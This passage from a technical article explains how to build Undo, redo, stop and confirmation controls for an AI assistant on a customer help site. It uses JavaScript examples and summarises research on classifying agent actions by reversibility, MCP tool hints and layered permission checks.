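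Much software relied on confirmation boxes instead. In *To Confirm is Useless, to Undo Divine* (2005), David Platt complained to Microsoft's developers that programs ask "are you sure?" so often that nobody pays attention. In *Never Use a Warning When you Mean Undo* (2007), published in A List Apart, the designer Aza Raskin explained that closing a window and clicking "Okay" become a single habit, so people click before they think about the question. He thought making the question harder to ignore helped little. The game Guild Wars, for example, had players type a character's name before deleting it, which made them concentrate on the typing rather than the decision. Raskin preferred Gmail's approach of deleting the message at once, showing an Undo link, and keeping the message in the trash for people who noticed their mistake later.

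Raskin argued from examples and ran no experiment. Readers replied with hard cases, such as what Undo should do when several people edit the same document. A chatbot creates the same problem even when only one person is using the page, because the customer and the assistant both change it.

Researchers have since applied the idea to language models. GoEX, a 2024 system that *EvoUndo* (2026) summarises, lets a model act before someone checks the result. If the result is wrong, the software either reverses the action or has already limited the possible damage.

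### The undo record and the check

An undo record should contain the action, the customer's request number, the old and new values, and how to restore the old one. When the customer presses Undo, the code checks whether the current value still matches the saved new value. If it does, the code restores the old value. If not, something else has changed the setting since, so the code leaves it alone and notifies the customer.

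```js
const root = document.documentElement;
const settings = {
  theme: {
    read: () => root.getAttribute("data-theme"),
    write: v => v === null
      ? root.removeAttribute("data-theme")
      : root.setAttribute("data-theme", v)
  }
};
const log = [];

function change(request, name, next) {
  const setting = settings[name];
  const record = { request, name, before: setting.read(), after: next };
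  log.push(record);
  setting.write(next);
  record.after = setting.read();
}

function undo({ name, before, after }) {
  const setting = settings[name];
  if (setting.read() !== after) return { name, undone: false };
  setting.write(before);
  return { name, undone: setting.read() === before };
}
```

The record needs only the setting's name, because `settings` holds the code that reads and writes that setting. The handler saves the record before it writes the new value, so a crash between the two steps can't leave a change without a record. After writing the value, the handler reads it back in case the site stored something slightly different.

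Suppose the customer has never chosen a theme and is typing in the complaint form. Their seventh request is "Show me the refund rules, in dark mode." They then find the dark page hard to read and choose high contrast from the site's own menu.

| Step | Theme | Place on the page | Undo records for request 7 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Before the request | None stored, page light | Complaint form | None |
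| Assistant sets the theme | Dark | Complaint form | Theme: none → dark |
| Assistant scrolls | Dark | Refund rules | Theme: none → dark. Place: form → refund rules |
| Customer picks high contrast | High contrast | Refund rules | Unchanged |
| Customer presses Undo | **High contrast** | Complaint form | Place restored, theme left alone |

The check keeps Undo from removing the stored theme, which would return a customer who may need high contrast to the light page. The site can then display, "Returned to the complaint form. Your high-contrast theme is unchanged." A button beside this message can still restore the original theme for a customer who wants everything undone.

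The check has to be looser for scrolling. Anyone who reads the refund rules moves the page a little, so the position almost never matches exactly. Scrolling back to the form destroys nothing, so the code can skip the comparison.

Comparing values can also miss a change. If the customer switches from dark to light and then back to dark, the current value equals the saved "after" value, and Undo removes a theme that the customer chose. To avoid this, the site can keep a counter that goes up whenever anyone changes the setting, and compare counters instead. JavaScript also treats two lists with the same contents as different, so for a list of search filters the code must compare the contents or use a counter.

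### Saved values and inverse operations

Shneiderman described two ways to undo a change. A program can offer an *inverse operation*, such as moving right after moving left, or a command that restores the previous state from a saved copy, called a *snapshot*.

Restoring a snapshot is exact when the state is a single value. If the assistant enlarges 16-pixel text by 10%, the text becomes 17.6 pixels. Reducing that by 10% gives 15.84 pixels, while restoring the saved value gives 16.

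Inverse operations work better for lists that the customer also edits. Suppose the help site's article search is filtered to "English", the assistant adds "billing", and the customer adds "2026":

| Way of undoing | Filters afterwards | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Restore the snapshot | English | The customer's "2026" is gone |
| Restore only if the list is unchanged | English, billing, 2026 | Nothing lost, but "billing" stays |
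| Remove "billing" | English, 2026 | Only the assistant's change is gone |

Removing the "billing" filter is right only if the assistant added it. If the customer had already switched it on, the assistant's call changed nothing, and undoing it would remove the customer's choice. The record therefore has to include whether the filter was there before.

An inverse action can also reverse the wrong change if it selects its target by position. *Can You Undo It?* tested this with Git, which programmers use to keep successive versions of their files. An agent saved a version, a colleague saved another, and the researchers then ran a command that goes back one version. The command removed the colleague's version from the branch and left the agent's in place. When the researchers added a check that the newest version was still the agent's, the undo stopped and the colleague's work stayed. An Undo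 button that calls `history.back()` has the same fault as the unchecked command.

Checking that a system looks the same as before is a poor test of whether an undo worked. In the paper's database trials, an agent created a table, someone else added a row to it, and the undo deleted the table. This returned the database to its original state but also deleted the added row.

A more careful undo restored a row's old value only if the row still held the agent's value. Edits to other rows didn't block the undo, and an edit to the same row was left in place. This applies the theme check to each row separately. Checking smaller pieces leads to fewer conflicts, so the help site should keep one record per filter.

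### When the customer has kept writing

Changes to text are harder to undo, because people add to it in many places. Suppose the assistant corrects the date of the double charge in the complaint's first paragraph, and the customer then adds a paragraph about a bank fee. Restoring the text saved before the correction would also delete the new paragraph.

*Can You Undo It?* compared three ways of undoing an agent's edit to a file. The first restored the whole snapshot, and the second did so only if the file had not changed since the edit. The third, a *three-way merge*, compares the text before the edit, the text just after it and the current text, so that it can remove the agent's edit and keep later ones. The researchers tried each method on four small files in four situations, for 48 observations in total.

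| What happened after the agent's edit | Whole snapshot | Restore only if unchanged | Three-way merge |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing | Original text back | Original text back | Original text back |
| Someone edited another paragraph | **Later work erased** | No undo, later work kept | Agent's edit removed, later work kept |
| Someone edited the same line | **Later work erased** | No undo, later work kept | No undo, later work kept |

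In the fourth situation, the software couldn't save the earlier text, so it didn't let the agent edit the file. The help site could follow the same rule and make only changes it can save a record for.

The four files differed only in their characters and line endings and gave identical results every time, so the 48 observations are weaker evidence than 48 independent tests would be. The researchers also made the edits one after another, but a customer may type while the undo is running, so the site's code must check the text immediately before it writes.

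A merge is worth the extra work for the complaint. If the customer has rewritten the same line, the site can show the old and new versions side by side and let them choose.

### Undoing a whole request, or just part of it

A customer who made one request probably expects one press of Undo to reverse all of it, which is why each record includes the request number:

```js
function undoRequest(request) {
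  return log.filter(r => r.request === request).reverse().map(undo);
}
```

The `reverse()` matters when one request changes the same setting twice. Suppose the assistant sets the theme to dark and then to high contrast. Undoing the changes in reverse order returns the theme to dark and then clears the stored theme. In the original order, the check on the first record fails because the page is no longer dark. The code then undoes only the second change, which leaves the theme dark instead of clearing it.

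*Building Effective AI Coding Agents for the Terminal* (2026) describes OpenDev, a programming agent in which each undo reverses the latest file operation. The undo deletes a file the agent created or restores one the agent changed or deleted. On the help site, the customer would press undo once for the scroll and once for the theme. This would give the customer more control, but the tool that ran last would determine which change is undone first.

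OpenDev's log covers only changes that the agent makes through its file tools, so the system also takes a full copy of the files at every step that modifies them. The help site has no such backup, so every write has to go through `change`. If its `set_theme` handler also saves the theme to the customer's account by some other route, Undo will restore the colours on the screen but not the saved preference.

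Google's Agent Development Kit, a toolkit for building agents, can rewind a session to an earlier request. *ChronoMem* (2026) points out that this does not restore data that belongs to the user's account or the whole application, or anything outside the toolkit. After a rewind, a customer could find the conversation back at request 6 but the account still in dark mode.

*Selective undo* reverses an earlier request and keeps the later ones. The check covers most cases, but it needs help when two requests changed the same setting. Suppose request 7 set the theme to dark and request 9 set it to high contrast. The customer undoes request 7, and the theme stays at high contrast, which is right. If they later undo request 9, its record restores dark, which they have already rejected. The code can prevent this by passing the older "before" value on to the later record:

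| Step | Record 7 | Record 9 | Theme |
|---|---|---|---|
| After both requests | None → dark | Dark → high contrast | High contrast |
| Customer undoes request 7 | Removed | **None** → high contrast | High contrast |
| Customer undoes request 9 | Removed | Removed | None stored |

*NaSh* (Gyawali, Kallas and colleagues, 2025) proposes selective undo for a command line that takes requests in ordinary language. The paper describes a design and reports no measurements. The system would save the old version of every file a command changes, so the user could undo one command, or restore just one of the files it changed, and keep later changes. It would detect conflicts by comparing version numbers.

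Some conflicts would still go undetected. If one command installs a software package and a later command installs another that depends on it, undoing the first breaks the second, even though the two commands changed none of the same files. Gyawali and colleagues think that catching this would require tracing every file that each program reads. A help site has hidden dependencies too, though fewer. If the assistant sets the country to Ireland and the customer then picks a refund method that exists only there, undoing the country change leaves a method that isn't available in the selected country.

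### How long Undo lasts

In NaSh, the user can keep old versions until the disk fills up. Deleting them is like emptying a recycle bin, after which the user can no longer undo those changes. The system could also delete the oldest versions automatically. Raskin's readers suggested much shorter limits, such as a ten-second countdown next to the Undo link. Ten seconds is too short for a customer whose screen reader has to read the message before they can reach the link.

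The help site can keep records of scrolls and theme changes in session storage, where they survive a full page load and last until the customer closes the tab. This works because each record is plain data, and the new page supplies the code that restores the value. A record containing an old draft or address should expire as early as a saved draft does.

Some limits on undoing an action come from other companies' systems. Gyawali and colleagues propose that every call to an outside service should return the conditions for undoing it, including any deadline and the information needed to start the undo. The service's developers would write an undo function for each function they offer. If a service relies on others, it would combine their conditions and return the earliest deadline.

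Suppose the help site has a tool that books a phone call with the billing team. The calendar accepts cancellations until 17:00 on Wednesday, but the team fixes its schedule at 15:30, so 15:30 is the limit. The tool could return:

```json
{
  "booked": "Thursday 10:00",
  "undo": {
    "tool": "cancel_call",
    "id": "call-4821",
    "until": "Wednesday 15:30",
    "remains": "confirmation text message"
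  }
}
```

The site can then show a "Cancel call" button and remove it at 15:30. "Undo" would be the wrong label, because the customer has already received the text message. Gyawali and colleagues mention a similar case, in which cloud services can reverse an action but not the payment for it.

The proposal depends on the supplier returning a deadline. If it doesn't, the developer has to look up the limit in the supplier's terms, write it into the handler, and keep it up to date.

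### Redo

A customer who presses Undo by mistake needs a way forward again. With the records above, redo is the same function with the two values swapped:

```js
function redo({ name, before, after }) {
  return undo({ name, before: after, after: before });
}
```

The check still applies, so Redo sets the dark theme only if the page still has the theme that Undo restored. Redo should not send the customer's request to the model again, because the model might choose a different theme or section. *AgentRewind* (2026) avoids the same problem when it returns an agent to an earlier point. It restores the conversation and the state of the controlled environment together, and reads the model's earlier outputs and the tools' results from a log instead of calling the model or running the tools again.

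Redo doesn't suit bookings or messages. Rebooking the cancelled phone call creates a new call, perhaps at another time, and sends another text message, so the site should treat it as a new action.

### Why the Undo button should not need the model

When the customer presses Undo, the site's code should restore the saved values without asking the model. Asking the model to "put it back" can take several seconds and fails if the connection is down. The model may also restore the wrong value, as in the theme example, where it had no way to return to "follow the system".

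Wang and Qi (2026), in *Recoverability and Verifier Strength*, compared restoring a saved copy with having a model write the reversal. They studied changes to an agent's written instructions, not to a web page, and tested the agent on simulated airline customer service. Even an unchanged agent, run twice, got the same result on only about 95% of tasks, because its behaviour varies from run to run. After they restored the old instructions from a saved copy, the agent matched its original results just as often. When a model wrote the reversal, agreement was 16 percentage points lower. They tested only three such reversals, but all three differed measurably from the original.

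The changed instructions altered the outcome of 17% of tasks beyond the normal variation, and restoring the old instructions exactly did not repair those outcomes. Suppose the assistant on the help site applies a filter that hides half of the refund rules, and the customer sends a complaint based on what they can see. Undoing the filter brings the rules back but does not correct the complaint.

Customers will also type "undo that" into the chat. The site can give the model an `undo_request` tool that takes a request number and runs the same code as the button. The model then only picks which request to undo.

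The model also has to be told what the button did, or it may tell the customer that the page is still dark. Deleting the original calls from the conversation, so that it looks as if nothing happened, can be risky. In *Cleaning an Agent's History Hurts When the World Still Holds the Error*, Pakhomov, Pang and colleagues (2026) stopped agents partway through a task, changed either the agent's history or the state of the system, and had a model continue from there. Removing a mistake from the history could leave the agent worse off than no edit at all if the mistake was still there in the system.

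In the worked example, the theme stayed at high contrast, so deleting the theme call would give the model a false history. The site should keep the old calls and add an accurate entry:

```
undo   {"request": 7, "place": "restored",
        "theme": "not restored, user chose high-contrast"}
```

### Stopping halfway

If the customer presses Stop after the theme has changed but before the page scrolls, the code should cancel the scroll and keep the theme, since the customer may have wanted only the theme change. The site can show, "Stopped. The theme had already changed to dark · Undo."

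The difficulty is a call that arrives late. The model may already be writing its next tool call when the customer presses Stop, and the call then reaches a page that no longer expects it. Yang, Pu and colleagues (2026), in *Task-State Governance*, handle this with a number they call an *epoch*. It goes up whenever the user pauses the agent and revises the task, and the software discards any action that the model proposed under an older number. The help site can do the same:

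```js
let epoch = 0;
stopButton.onclick = () => { epoch += 1; };

async function runCalls(calls, sentIn) {
  for (const call of calls) {
    if (sentIn !== epoch) return { stopped: true, notRun: call.name };
    await handlers[call.name](call.args);
  }
}
```

Here `sentIn` is the epoch at the moment the customer sent the message. The code checks it before every call, so a Stop during the theme change still prevents the scroll. A handler that waits for something, such as late content, should check again after the wait. This check can't undo an action that has already gone out, as Yang and colleagues acknowledge. If the handler has already sent the request to book a phone call, the site has to find out whether the booking succeeded and, if it did, offer to cancel it.

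### TaskVM

Yang and colleagues built the epoch number into TaskVM, an experimental system for agents that work in several applications by clicking and typing. In their example, a project briefing moves by one day. The calendar entry and the announcement to the team must change, but a flight booking must not. A list of the agent's planned clicks can't include the requirement that the booking stay the same.

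TaskVM therefore represents a task as three sets of facts. The *desired state* is what the user wants to be true, such as the briefing being on Thursday. The *preserved state* is what must not change, such as the flight. The *observed state* is what the applications currently show. The user can edit the desired and preserved values next to the live application, and the task counts as complete only when the observed state matches both.

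A separate call to the model decides whether the agent has finished. It looks at new screenshots without seeing the agent's reasoning, and needs visible evidence that the change took place. This prevents the agent from counting something that was already true as its own change. However, the same model, GPT-5.6 Sol, does both jobs, so the check can repeat the agent's mistake. A page can also fail to show the real state of the system behind it. Yang and colleagues give the example of a booking page that shows a new date although the airline has not processed the refund.

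When the user asks for a rollback, TaskVM plans the reversal from the actions it has recorded. It clicks a checkbox back or clears a draft field, sends a cancellation to offset a message, and marks a completed payment as irreversible. The user sees a preview of this plan before the rollback starts.

Yang and colleagues compared TaskVM with two agents that used the same model, one that acted directly on screenshots and another that wrote a plan first. Each tried 36 tasks in simulated applications.

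| | TaskVM | Direct agent | Planning agent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tasks that met every condition | 21 of 36 | 18 of 36 | 17 of 36 |
| Average share of conditions met | 87.0% | 76.1% | 73.7% |
| Earlier state restored on request | 4 of 6 | 0 of 3 | 0 of 5 |
| Calls to the model | 1,126 | 1,361 | 1,031 |
| Average time per task | 554 s | 250 s | 186 s |

TaskVM's lead of three or four tasks could easily be chance, and the researchers based the tasks on TaskVM's design, which probably favours it. The other two agents' errors are more informative. The direct agent often stopped before a page had saved its change, and the planning agent altered neighbouring form fields when it revised its plan.

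TaskVM rolled back successfully in four of six attempts, and the other agents in none. The gap is less impressive than it looks because the other agents had no restore command and did not manage to improvise a rollback. In 18 harder tests, TaskVM's only failure was also a rollback, which it could not complete because a signing window and the confirming click interfered with each other. Yang and colleagues had not fixed this when they published.

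TaskVM took more than twice as long as the direct agent. Part of the extra time comes from working in other companies' applications, where the system has to read everything from the screen. The help site's code can read its own theme and form directly, so it can check almost instantly that an action preserved what it should have. For example, the site can copy the complaint text before every page action and compare it afterwards. That would have caught the highlighting code erasing the form when it rebuilt the page section.

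Yang and colleagues also ran a study with 37 people, mostly students and researchers. Each participant supervised an agent both through TaskVM and through an ordinary chat window. The agent's actions were prerecorded, so its steps and mistakes were the same in both.

| | TaskVM | Chat window |
|---|---|---|
| Perceived control over recovery, out of 7 | 5.56 | 4.63 |
| Trust, out of 7 | 5.54 | 4.36 |
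| People who rolled something back | 11 | 2 |
| Successful interventions by the end of the task | 18 of 35 | 18 of 35 |
| Median time to intervene | 85 s | 66 s |

The differences in perceived control and trust were statistically significant, but the difference in time was not. Participants rolled back 17 times with TaskVM, 13 of them in tasks that never prompted them to undo anything, so people used the function when they could see it.

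The study measured how much control people felt they had under replayed execution, but did not test whether they could recover from a live agent's mistakes. People felt more in control with TaskVM, but their interventions succeeded equally often with both interfaces. The added feeling of control may not be purely a benefit, since extra trust could make people check less. The study found slight evidence against this concern. People were about 70% confident in their answers about the state of the task with both interfaces, but they got all the answers right 57% of the time with TaskVM and 45% with the chat window. That comparison used only about 20 responses per interface.

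Fourteen participants came back to try TaskVM on their own tasks with a live model. They reported little effort, but they had already found TaskVM much easier than the chat window, while those who did not return had found no difference. Two of the fourteen asked for automatic restore points wherever a failure was likely. On the help site, `change` already saves a record before every change, so customers would not have to predict when they might need one.

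## Which actions to allow, ask about or withhold

Undo can restore the customer's old theme, but it can't recall a complaint that staff have already read. The help site's developers therefore have to decide in advance which actions the assistant may take at once, which need a *confirmation* (a question the software shows the user before an action runs), and which to withhold. They can sensibly start by considering how well the customer could recover from a mistake.

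### Five classes of action

*Can You Undo It?* sorts tool calls into five classes by what it takes to recover from them, with a suggested policy for each. The last column applies them to the help site.

| Class | Criterion | Suggested policy | Help-site example |
|---|---|---|---|
| R0, no effect | The call changes nothing outside the agent | Act | Searching the articles |
| R1, restorable | Somebody recorded the earlier state, whoever is acting can write it back, and no outsider has seen the change | Act, then notify | Changing the theme after saving the old one |
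| R2, compensable | A known further action leads to an acceptable state at a limited, known cost | Ask, or stay within a budget the user approved earlier | Booking a phone call that the customer can cancel |
| R3, hard to recover | Recovery takes another person, an outside process or unlimited effort; changes to access and passwords also belong here | Ask every time | Changing the account's email address |
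| R4, irreversible | Nobody can recall or offset the effect | Never act autonomously | Deleting the account for good |

A user can still explicitly authorise an R4 action. The software published with the paper is simpler than the table. It asks the user about every action at R2 or above and leaves R0 and R1 to the product's existing rules.

Each call is classed by its worst effect, and a call that the software doesn't recognise counts as R4. If the developers forget to classify a new tool, the chatbot asks customers before using it, even when it doesn't need to, instead of risking an action they didn't want.

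The same tool can fall into different classes depending on its arguments. A rule that moves a call to a less restricted class should match a specific harmless form of the call, not just check that no obviously dangerous word appears. For example, a database command that starts with `SELECT` normally only reads data, but it can call a function that changes data. On the help site, the rule for a `change_setting` tool should accept "language" and "text size" by name, because a rule that accepts everything except "email" would also accept any sensitive setting added later.

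Developers can also move an action down to R1 by saving the earlier state. The software must confirm that the copy was saved before the call runs, and if saving fails, the higher class applies. The `openArticle` handler shown earlier works this way, leaving the page only if it has saved the complaint. Saving a copy never lowers the class of a disclosure, because restoring the earlier state doesn't erase what a reader has learned.

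### Other ways to classify actions

*Revisable by Design*, from April 2026, starts with the case of a user changing their mind while an agent is working. It sorts actions into four classes: idempotent, reversible, compensable and irreversible. It uses "idempotent" for actions that don't change the outside world, such as reading a file, but its formal definition is the usual, looser one, which also covers "Set theme to dark".

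An action's class determines what the agent must do when the user changes their mind. A read needs no undoing, and a reversible action needs one reversal. If a compensable action that conflicts with the new request has already run, the agent has to offset it, however well it plans. If the conflicting action was irreversible, the agent can't fully meet the new request. A better model doesn't help with this, but different tools or a different order of steps can.

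The paper also defines a *reversibility ratio*, the share of a task's tools that are idempotent or reversible. Suppose the help site has tools to search, change the theme, save a draft, book a call and submit a complaint. The first three qualify, so the ratio is 0.6. According to the paper, a run of ten steps should then contain at least four steps with unavoidable costs on average. This holds only if the agent uses every tool equally often and the new request conflicts with each of those steps. An assistant that searches nine times and books one call has one such step, so the ratio is a poor forecast for a particular request, though it describes the tool list fairly.

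Kang, Cho and colleagues (2026), in *POLAR*, use a score between 0 and 1 instead of classes. A person writes down, for each tool that changes something, how another tool could reverse it. Before a call runs, the software looks for a sequence of reversals and scores each step:

| How the step can be reversed | Score |
|---|---|
| Another tool reverses it exactly | w |
| It is reversible while some condition holds | w if the condition holds now, otherwise 0 |
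| Another tool compensates for it at a loss | w × (1 − loss) |
| It uses something up | 0 |
| It has an effect outside the system | 0 |

Here w is the author's confidence in the entry, at most 1. A sequence gets the score of its lowest-scoring step, and POLAR refuses any sequence that scores below 0.80.

Suppose the assistant changes the theme, which scores 1, and books a phone call. If the confidence is 0.95 and cancelling the call loses 10% of its value, the booking scores 0.95 × 0.9 = 0.855. The whole sequence also scores 0.855, so the assistant runs it without asking the user. Under the five classes, the booking is R2 and the assistant would have to ask. If cancelling loses 20%, the score is 0.76 and POLAR refuses.

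The three schemes classify a sent email differently. *Revisable by Design* calls it compensable, because the agent can send a correction. *Can You Undo It?* puts the intended delivery of content to outsiders in R4, even if the sender can delete the message afterwards. POLAR scores an outside effect 0. A correction solves the problem if the email had the wrong date, but not if it contained a card number. The class depends on the content, so the help site should use the strictest of the three classifications for any tool that sends free text.

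### What happened when POLAR refused actions

Kang and colleagues tested POLAR on simulated customer service, with six models and 150 attempted runs per model in each area. They measured each model's average task reward, from 0 to 1, and compared it with that of the same model without POLAR.

| Area | Models that did better with POLAR | Largest gain | Largest loss |
|---|---|---|---|
| Airline | 4 of 6 | +0.18 | −0.12 |
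| Retail | 1 of 6 | +0.03 | −0.24 |
| Telecom | 3 of 6 | +0.05 | −0.06 |

In the airline tasks, the two models that got worse were the two that had done best without POLAR. The largest loss was in retail, where the score of gpt-oss-120B, an open model from OpenAI, fell from 0.455 to 0.213. POLAR had blocked 150 of the model's attempts to return delivered items and 103 of its attempts to exchange them. Customers often have legitimate reasons to return items, and Kang and colleagues think the blocked attempts plausibly explain the loss.

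Even the airline gains are weak evidence for the scoring. In a separate test with one small model, the researchers switched off every kind of reversal except the exact ones. The airline rules contain no exact reversals, so POLAR blocked nearly every change the agent attempted. The score rose by 0.087, compared with 0.080 for the full scheme. The small model seems to have gained mainly from having its changes blocked, and the researchers say they haven't yet shown an advantage over a simple blocker. Task reward also doesn't measure how much harm POLAR prevented.

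Low reversibility is therefore a better reason to ask than to refuse. POLAR has a version that asks, but its records are too incomplete for a comparison. That version searches the user's recent messages for a word of consent, so it could mistake a "yes" to another question for consent. The help site should tie each answer to one action by giving that action its own button.

### Reversible actions can still do harm

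Suppose the customer says "stop sending me all these emails" and the assistant turns off every notification on the account. The site saves the old settings, so this action is R1. With notifications off, the site doesn't send its usual warning when the customer's card expires on Wednesday, and it suspends the account on Friday. Undo then restores every notification setting, but the account stays suspended.

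*Can You Undo It?* notes that compensable actions can cause serious harm or affect people before anyone offsets them. Its classes aren't meant to replace judging how severe an action is or whether the user authorised it. Reading can also cause harm, since a tool that only looks up an order history can put it on a screen that other people can see.

The opposite also happens. Sending the complaint is irreversible, and it is usually exactly what the customer came to do.

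It also matters how soon the customer would notice a mistake. A wrong theme is obvious at once, so an Undo button next to it is nearly always enough. A wrong notification setting can go unnoticed for months, and by then the button is gone. Both changes are R1, but the chatbot should ask before changing the notification setting and not before changing the theme.

### Labels on tools, and how far to trust them

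Software that didn't write a tool needs some way to guess its class. The Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common format for offering tools to language models, lets a tool's author attach *tool hints*, which are labels that software may use but can't take as proof. There are four that describe behaviour, according to the project's blog, Model Context Protocol (2026):

| Hint | Value if the author leaves it out | What software might do with it |
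|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | False | Skip the confirmation if true |
| `destructiveHint` | True | Warn the user if true |
| `idempotentHint` | False | Retry after a failure if true |
| `openWorldHint` | True | Check the tool's output for untrusted content if true |

The default values describe the riskiest kind of tool, but many tools come without hints, and products differ in how strictly they apply the defaults. A dishonest author can also label a file-deleting tool as read-only. Justin Spahr-Summers, one of MCP's creators, asked during the original review how software could use a label that can't be trusted. The blog recommends using hints from trusted sources to decide when to ask the user, and relying on network controls or isolation for anything that needs a guarantee.

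A site that writes its own tools doesn't have to worry about dishonest labels, but honest ones can be too coarse. *Can You Undo It?* translated the hints into its five classes. Read-only tools became R0. Of the rest, open-world tools became R4, closed-world destructive tools R3, and closed-world non-destructive tools R1. No combination of hints produces R2. The researchers then compared the result with their own registry of tools from MCP servers:

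| Class in the registry | Tools compared | Hints give the same class | Hints give a lower class | Hints give a higher class |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| R0 | 303 | 280 | 0 | 23 |
| R1 | 28 | 7 | 2 | 19 |
| R2 | 13 | 0 | 2 | 11 |
| R3 | 39 | 3 | 4 | 32 |
| R4 | 98 | 73 | 25 | 0 |
| All | 481 | 363 | 33 | 85 |

The hints differ from the registry for 118 of 481 tools. Most of the agreement comes from tools that only read. In the three middle classes, where the choice between acting and asking is hardest, the hints and the registry agree on 10 of 80 tools. Software that relied on the hints and asked the user before using any tool rated R2 or higher would fail to ask about 20 tools that need a question according to the registry, and would ask about 41 that don't. Ten tools that the registry rates as irreversible have a read-only hint.

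The registry is weak evidence too. The researchers drafted it with the help of AI, and one of the paper's two authors then reviewed 150 of its entries. He rated 148 tools and agreed with the registry on 75, choosing a higher class for 67 and a lower one for six. For 139 of the tools, he approved AI-proposed ratings in batches. The sample included all 31 tools that the registry put in R1, but he put only two tools from the whole sample there.

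Many of the differences came from assumptions, such as whether an outsider might have seen the change. The figure of 118 therefore measures disagreement between two unverified sets of labels, not how often hints are wrong. The reviewer and the registry disagreed most about R1, the class that lets an assistant act without asking. The help site's developers should put an action in R1 only after testing its undo.

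According to W3C's *WebML CG Teleconference* (2026), the minutes of a meeting on 14 May 2026, WebMCP's only hint that separated reading from writing at the time was `readOnlyHint`, and the group discussed adding one for reversible or consequential actions. Johann Hofmann, who had proposed the addition, said that drafting an email is reversible and sending it isn't, but that a calendar invitation to other people is hard to classify. The group decided to collect use cases first. By 1 September, the security advice from Chrome for Developers (2026) included a `consequentialHint` for actions such as booking travel or transferring money. The agent or browser can respond to this hint by asking the user to confirm, but the hint doesn't require it to.

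### Permission in five layers

No single label is reliable, so the help site needs several independent checks. Suppose the customer asks the assistant, "Switch me to the cheaper plan."

1. **Which tools exist.** If the site has neither a `change_plan` tool nor a general one such as `click` or `run_script`, the assistant can only explain the plans or give a link. This is the strongest control over the site's own assistant.
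2. **Which arguments the tool accepts.** `change_plan` takes one of the plan names and nothing else. If it also took an account number, the model could supply the wrong one, so the handler gets the account from the signed-in session.
3. **What the user's own role permits.** On a company account, perhaps only the billing administrator may change the plan. The assistant should never have more rights than the person using it, and the page shouldn't register the tool for anyone else.
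4. **What needs confirmation.** The page shows the old plan, the new plan, the price and the start date, and waits for the customer to click.
5. **What the server enforces.** The server checks the session, the role, the plan and the price again, whatever the browser has sent.

Servers often don't check the user's role. Some sites hide a button from ordinary members but accept the request behind it from anyone who is signed in. People rarely discover this because they don't see the button, but a tool that calls the same address directly will succeed on its first try. OpenAI warns that site tools may expose functions that the page doesn't otherwise offer.

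The browser's part of this fits in a short function, which the `runCalls` loop shown earlier can call instead of the handler:

```js
const policy = new Map([
  ["scroll_to", "act"],
  ["set_theme", "act"],
  ["open_article", "act"],
  ["change_plan", "ask"]
]);

async function gate(call) {
  const rule = policy.get(call.name);
  if (!rule) return { ran: false, reason: "not allowed" };
  const args = structuredClone(call.args);
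  if (rule === "ask" && !(await askCustomer(call.name, args))) {
    return { ran: false, reason: "customer declined" };
  }
  return handlers[call.name](args);
}
```

A tool that isn't in `policy` doesn't run. The code copies the arguments before it calls `askCustomer`, so the handler runs with the values the customer saw. If the customer presses Stop while the question is open, `askCustomer` should close the question and return `false`.

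The `gate` function guards only against the model's mistakes, because anyone can edit code in their own browser and a browser agent can press the site's buttons without calling the function. For the plan change, the server can create a one-time code for "this account, basic plan, €9 a month" when the page shows the question, and accept the change only with that code and those values. If the price changes before the customer clicks, the code no longer matches and the page has to ask again.

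The server still can't tell whether a person or an agent clicked. For the few actions where this matters, the site can ask for the customer's password again. OpenAI tells ChatGPT users to type passwords on the website itself and never into the conversation, so a user who follows that advice has to be present to enter the password.

### The assistant's own permissions

The assistant should not be able to change its own permissions or remove the Undo button. Few developers would build a tool to do either, but a general-purpose tool can accidentally allow both.

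Suppose `change_setting` covers every switch on the account page, including one labeled "Let the assistant change my plan without asking". A customer, annoyed by a question about the text size, types "stop asking me all the time", and the model turns that switch on. The customer did ask for something like this, but probably wasn't thinking of the plan. The site should leave that switch out of the tool and have customers change it by hand in the settings menu.

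Tools can also hide or break the Undo button. A `hide_element` tool could hide it, and a theme tool that accepts any colour could make it the same colour as its background. The highlighting code that rebuilds a section's HTML would leave the button on the screen but remove the code that makes it work. The developers can keep the button outside the part of the page that tools may change. After each action, their code can check that the button is still visible, as it does for a heading after a scroll, and reverse the action if it isn't. Tools should also be unable to delete undo records.

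### When a question is worth asking

A confirmation lets the customer catch a mistake before it has any effect, which may be the only chance with a payment or a message. Undo requires no extra step from the customer when the assistant is right, and it lets them judge the real result instead of a description of it. But both rely on the customer, who must read the confirmation or notice the mistake afterward.

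The earlier calculation of when to ask assumed that customers always answer correctly. Let *r* be the share of unwanted actions that customers refuse when the site asks. As before, *p* is the probability that the customer wants the action, L is the loss from a wrong one, and a question costs 0.5. Asking first is better than acting at once when:

```
(1 − p) × r × L > 0.5
r > 0.5 / ((1 − p) × L)
```

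With *p* at 0.9 and some made-up losses, this gives:

| Action | L | Customers must refuse at least |
|---|---|---|
| Scroll, with a button to go back | 1 | Never worth asking |
| Open a page and lose the complaint | 6 | 83% of unwanted actions |
| Send the complaint with a mistake in it | 20 | 25% |
| Buy the wrong thing | 200 | 2.5% |

Asking before a purchase is worthwhile even if customers approve 39 out of 40 wrong purchases, but asking before the complaint is lost is worthwhile only if nearly everyone reads the question. It is therefore better for the site to save the draft of the complaint without asking. Each unnecessary question also makes people less attentive to the next one, which lowers *r* for the purchase too.

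Under the rules in *Can You Undo It?*, even harmless recorded tasks would have triggered about 1.6 questions to the user each, and only 119 of the 770 that succeeded would have finished without any. These figures are projections, and the paper doesn't measure how people would have answered.

A high approval rate does not prove that customers are careless. If the assistant is right 95% of the time, customers who read every question carefully will approve 95% of them, only slightly fewer than customers who approve everything without reading. The site's operators need to know how often customers regret an approval. They can estimate this roughly by counting the customers who reverse an action, or contact support about it, soon after approving it.

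The MCP blog describes two groups of the protocol's users. Developers of autonomous agents feel that confirmations slow things down and prefer to isolate the agent so that its mistakes can't spread, while large companies want more detailed hints than MCP has. GitHub offers a read-only mode that removes the risky tools, so there is no need to ask about them, and about 17% of its users have turned it on.

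A help site can't isolate the assistant from the customer's real account, but it can postpone the risky step, as *Revisable by Design* recommends for irreversible steps in general. The assistant fills in the complaint form, and the customer reads the text there and presses Submit. This adds no extra confirmation question for the customer to get used to, because they would have pressed Submit anyway. Shopify's checkout tools likewise leave the order for the buyer to confirm.

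### Confirmation in ChatGPT and WebMCP

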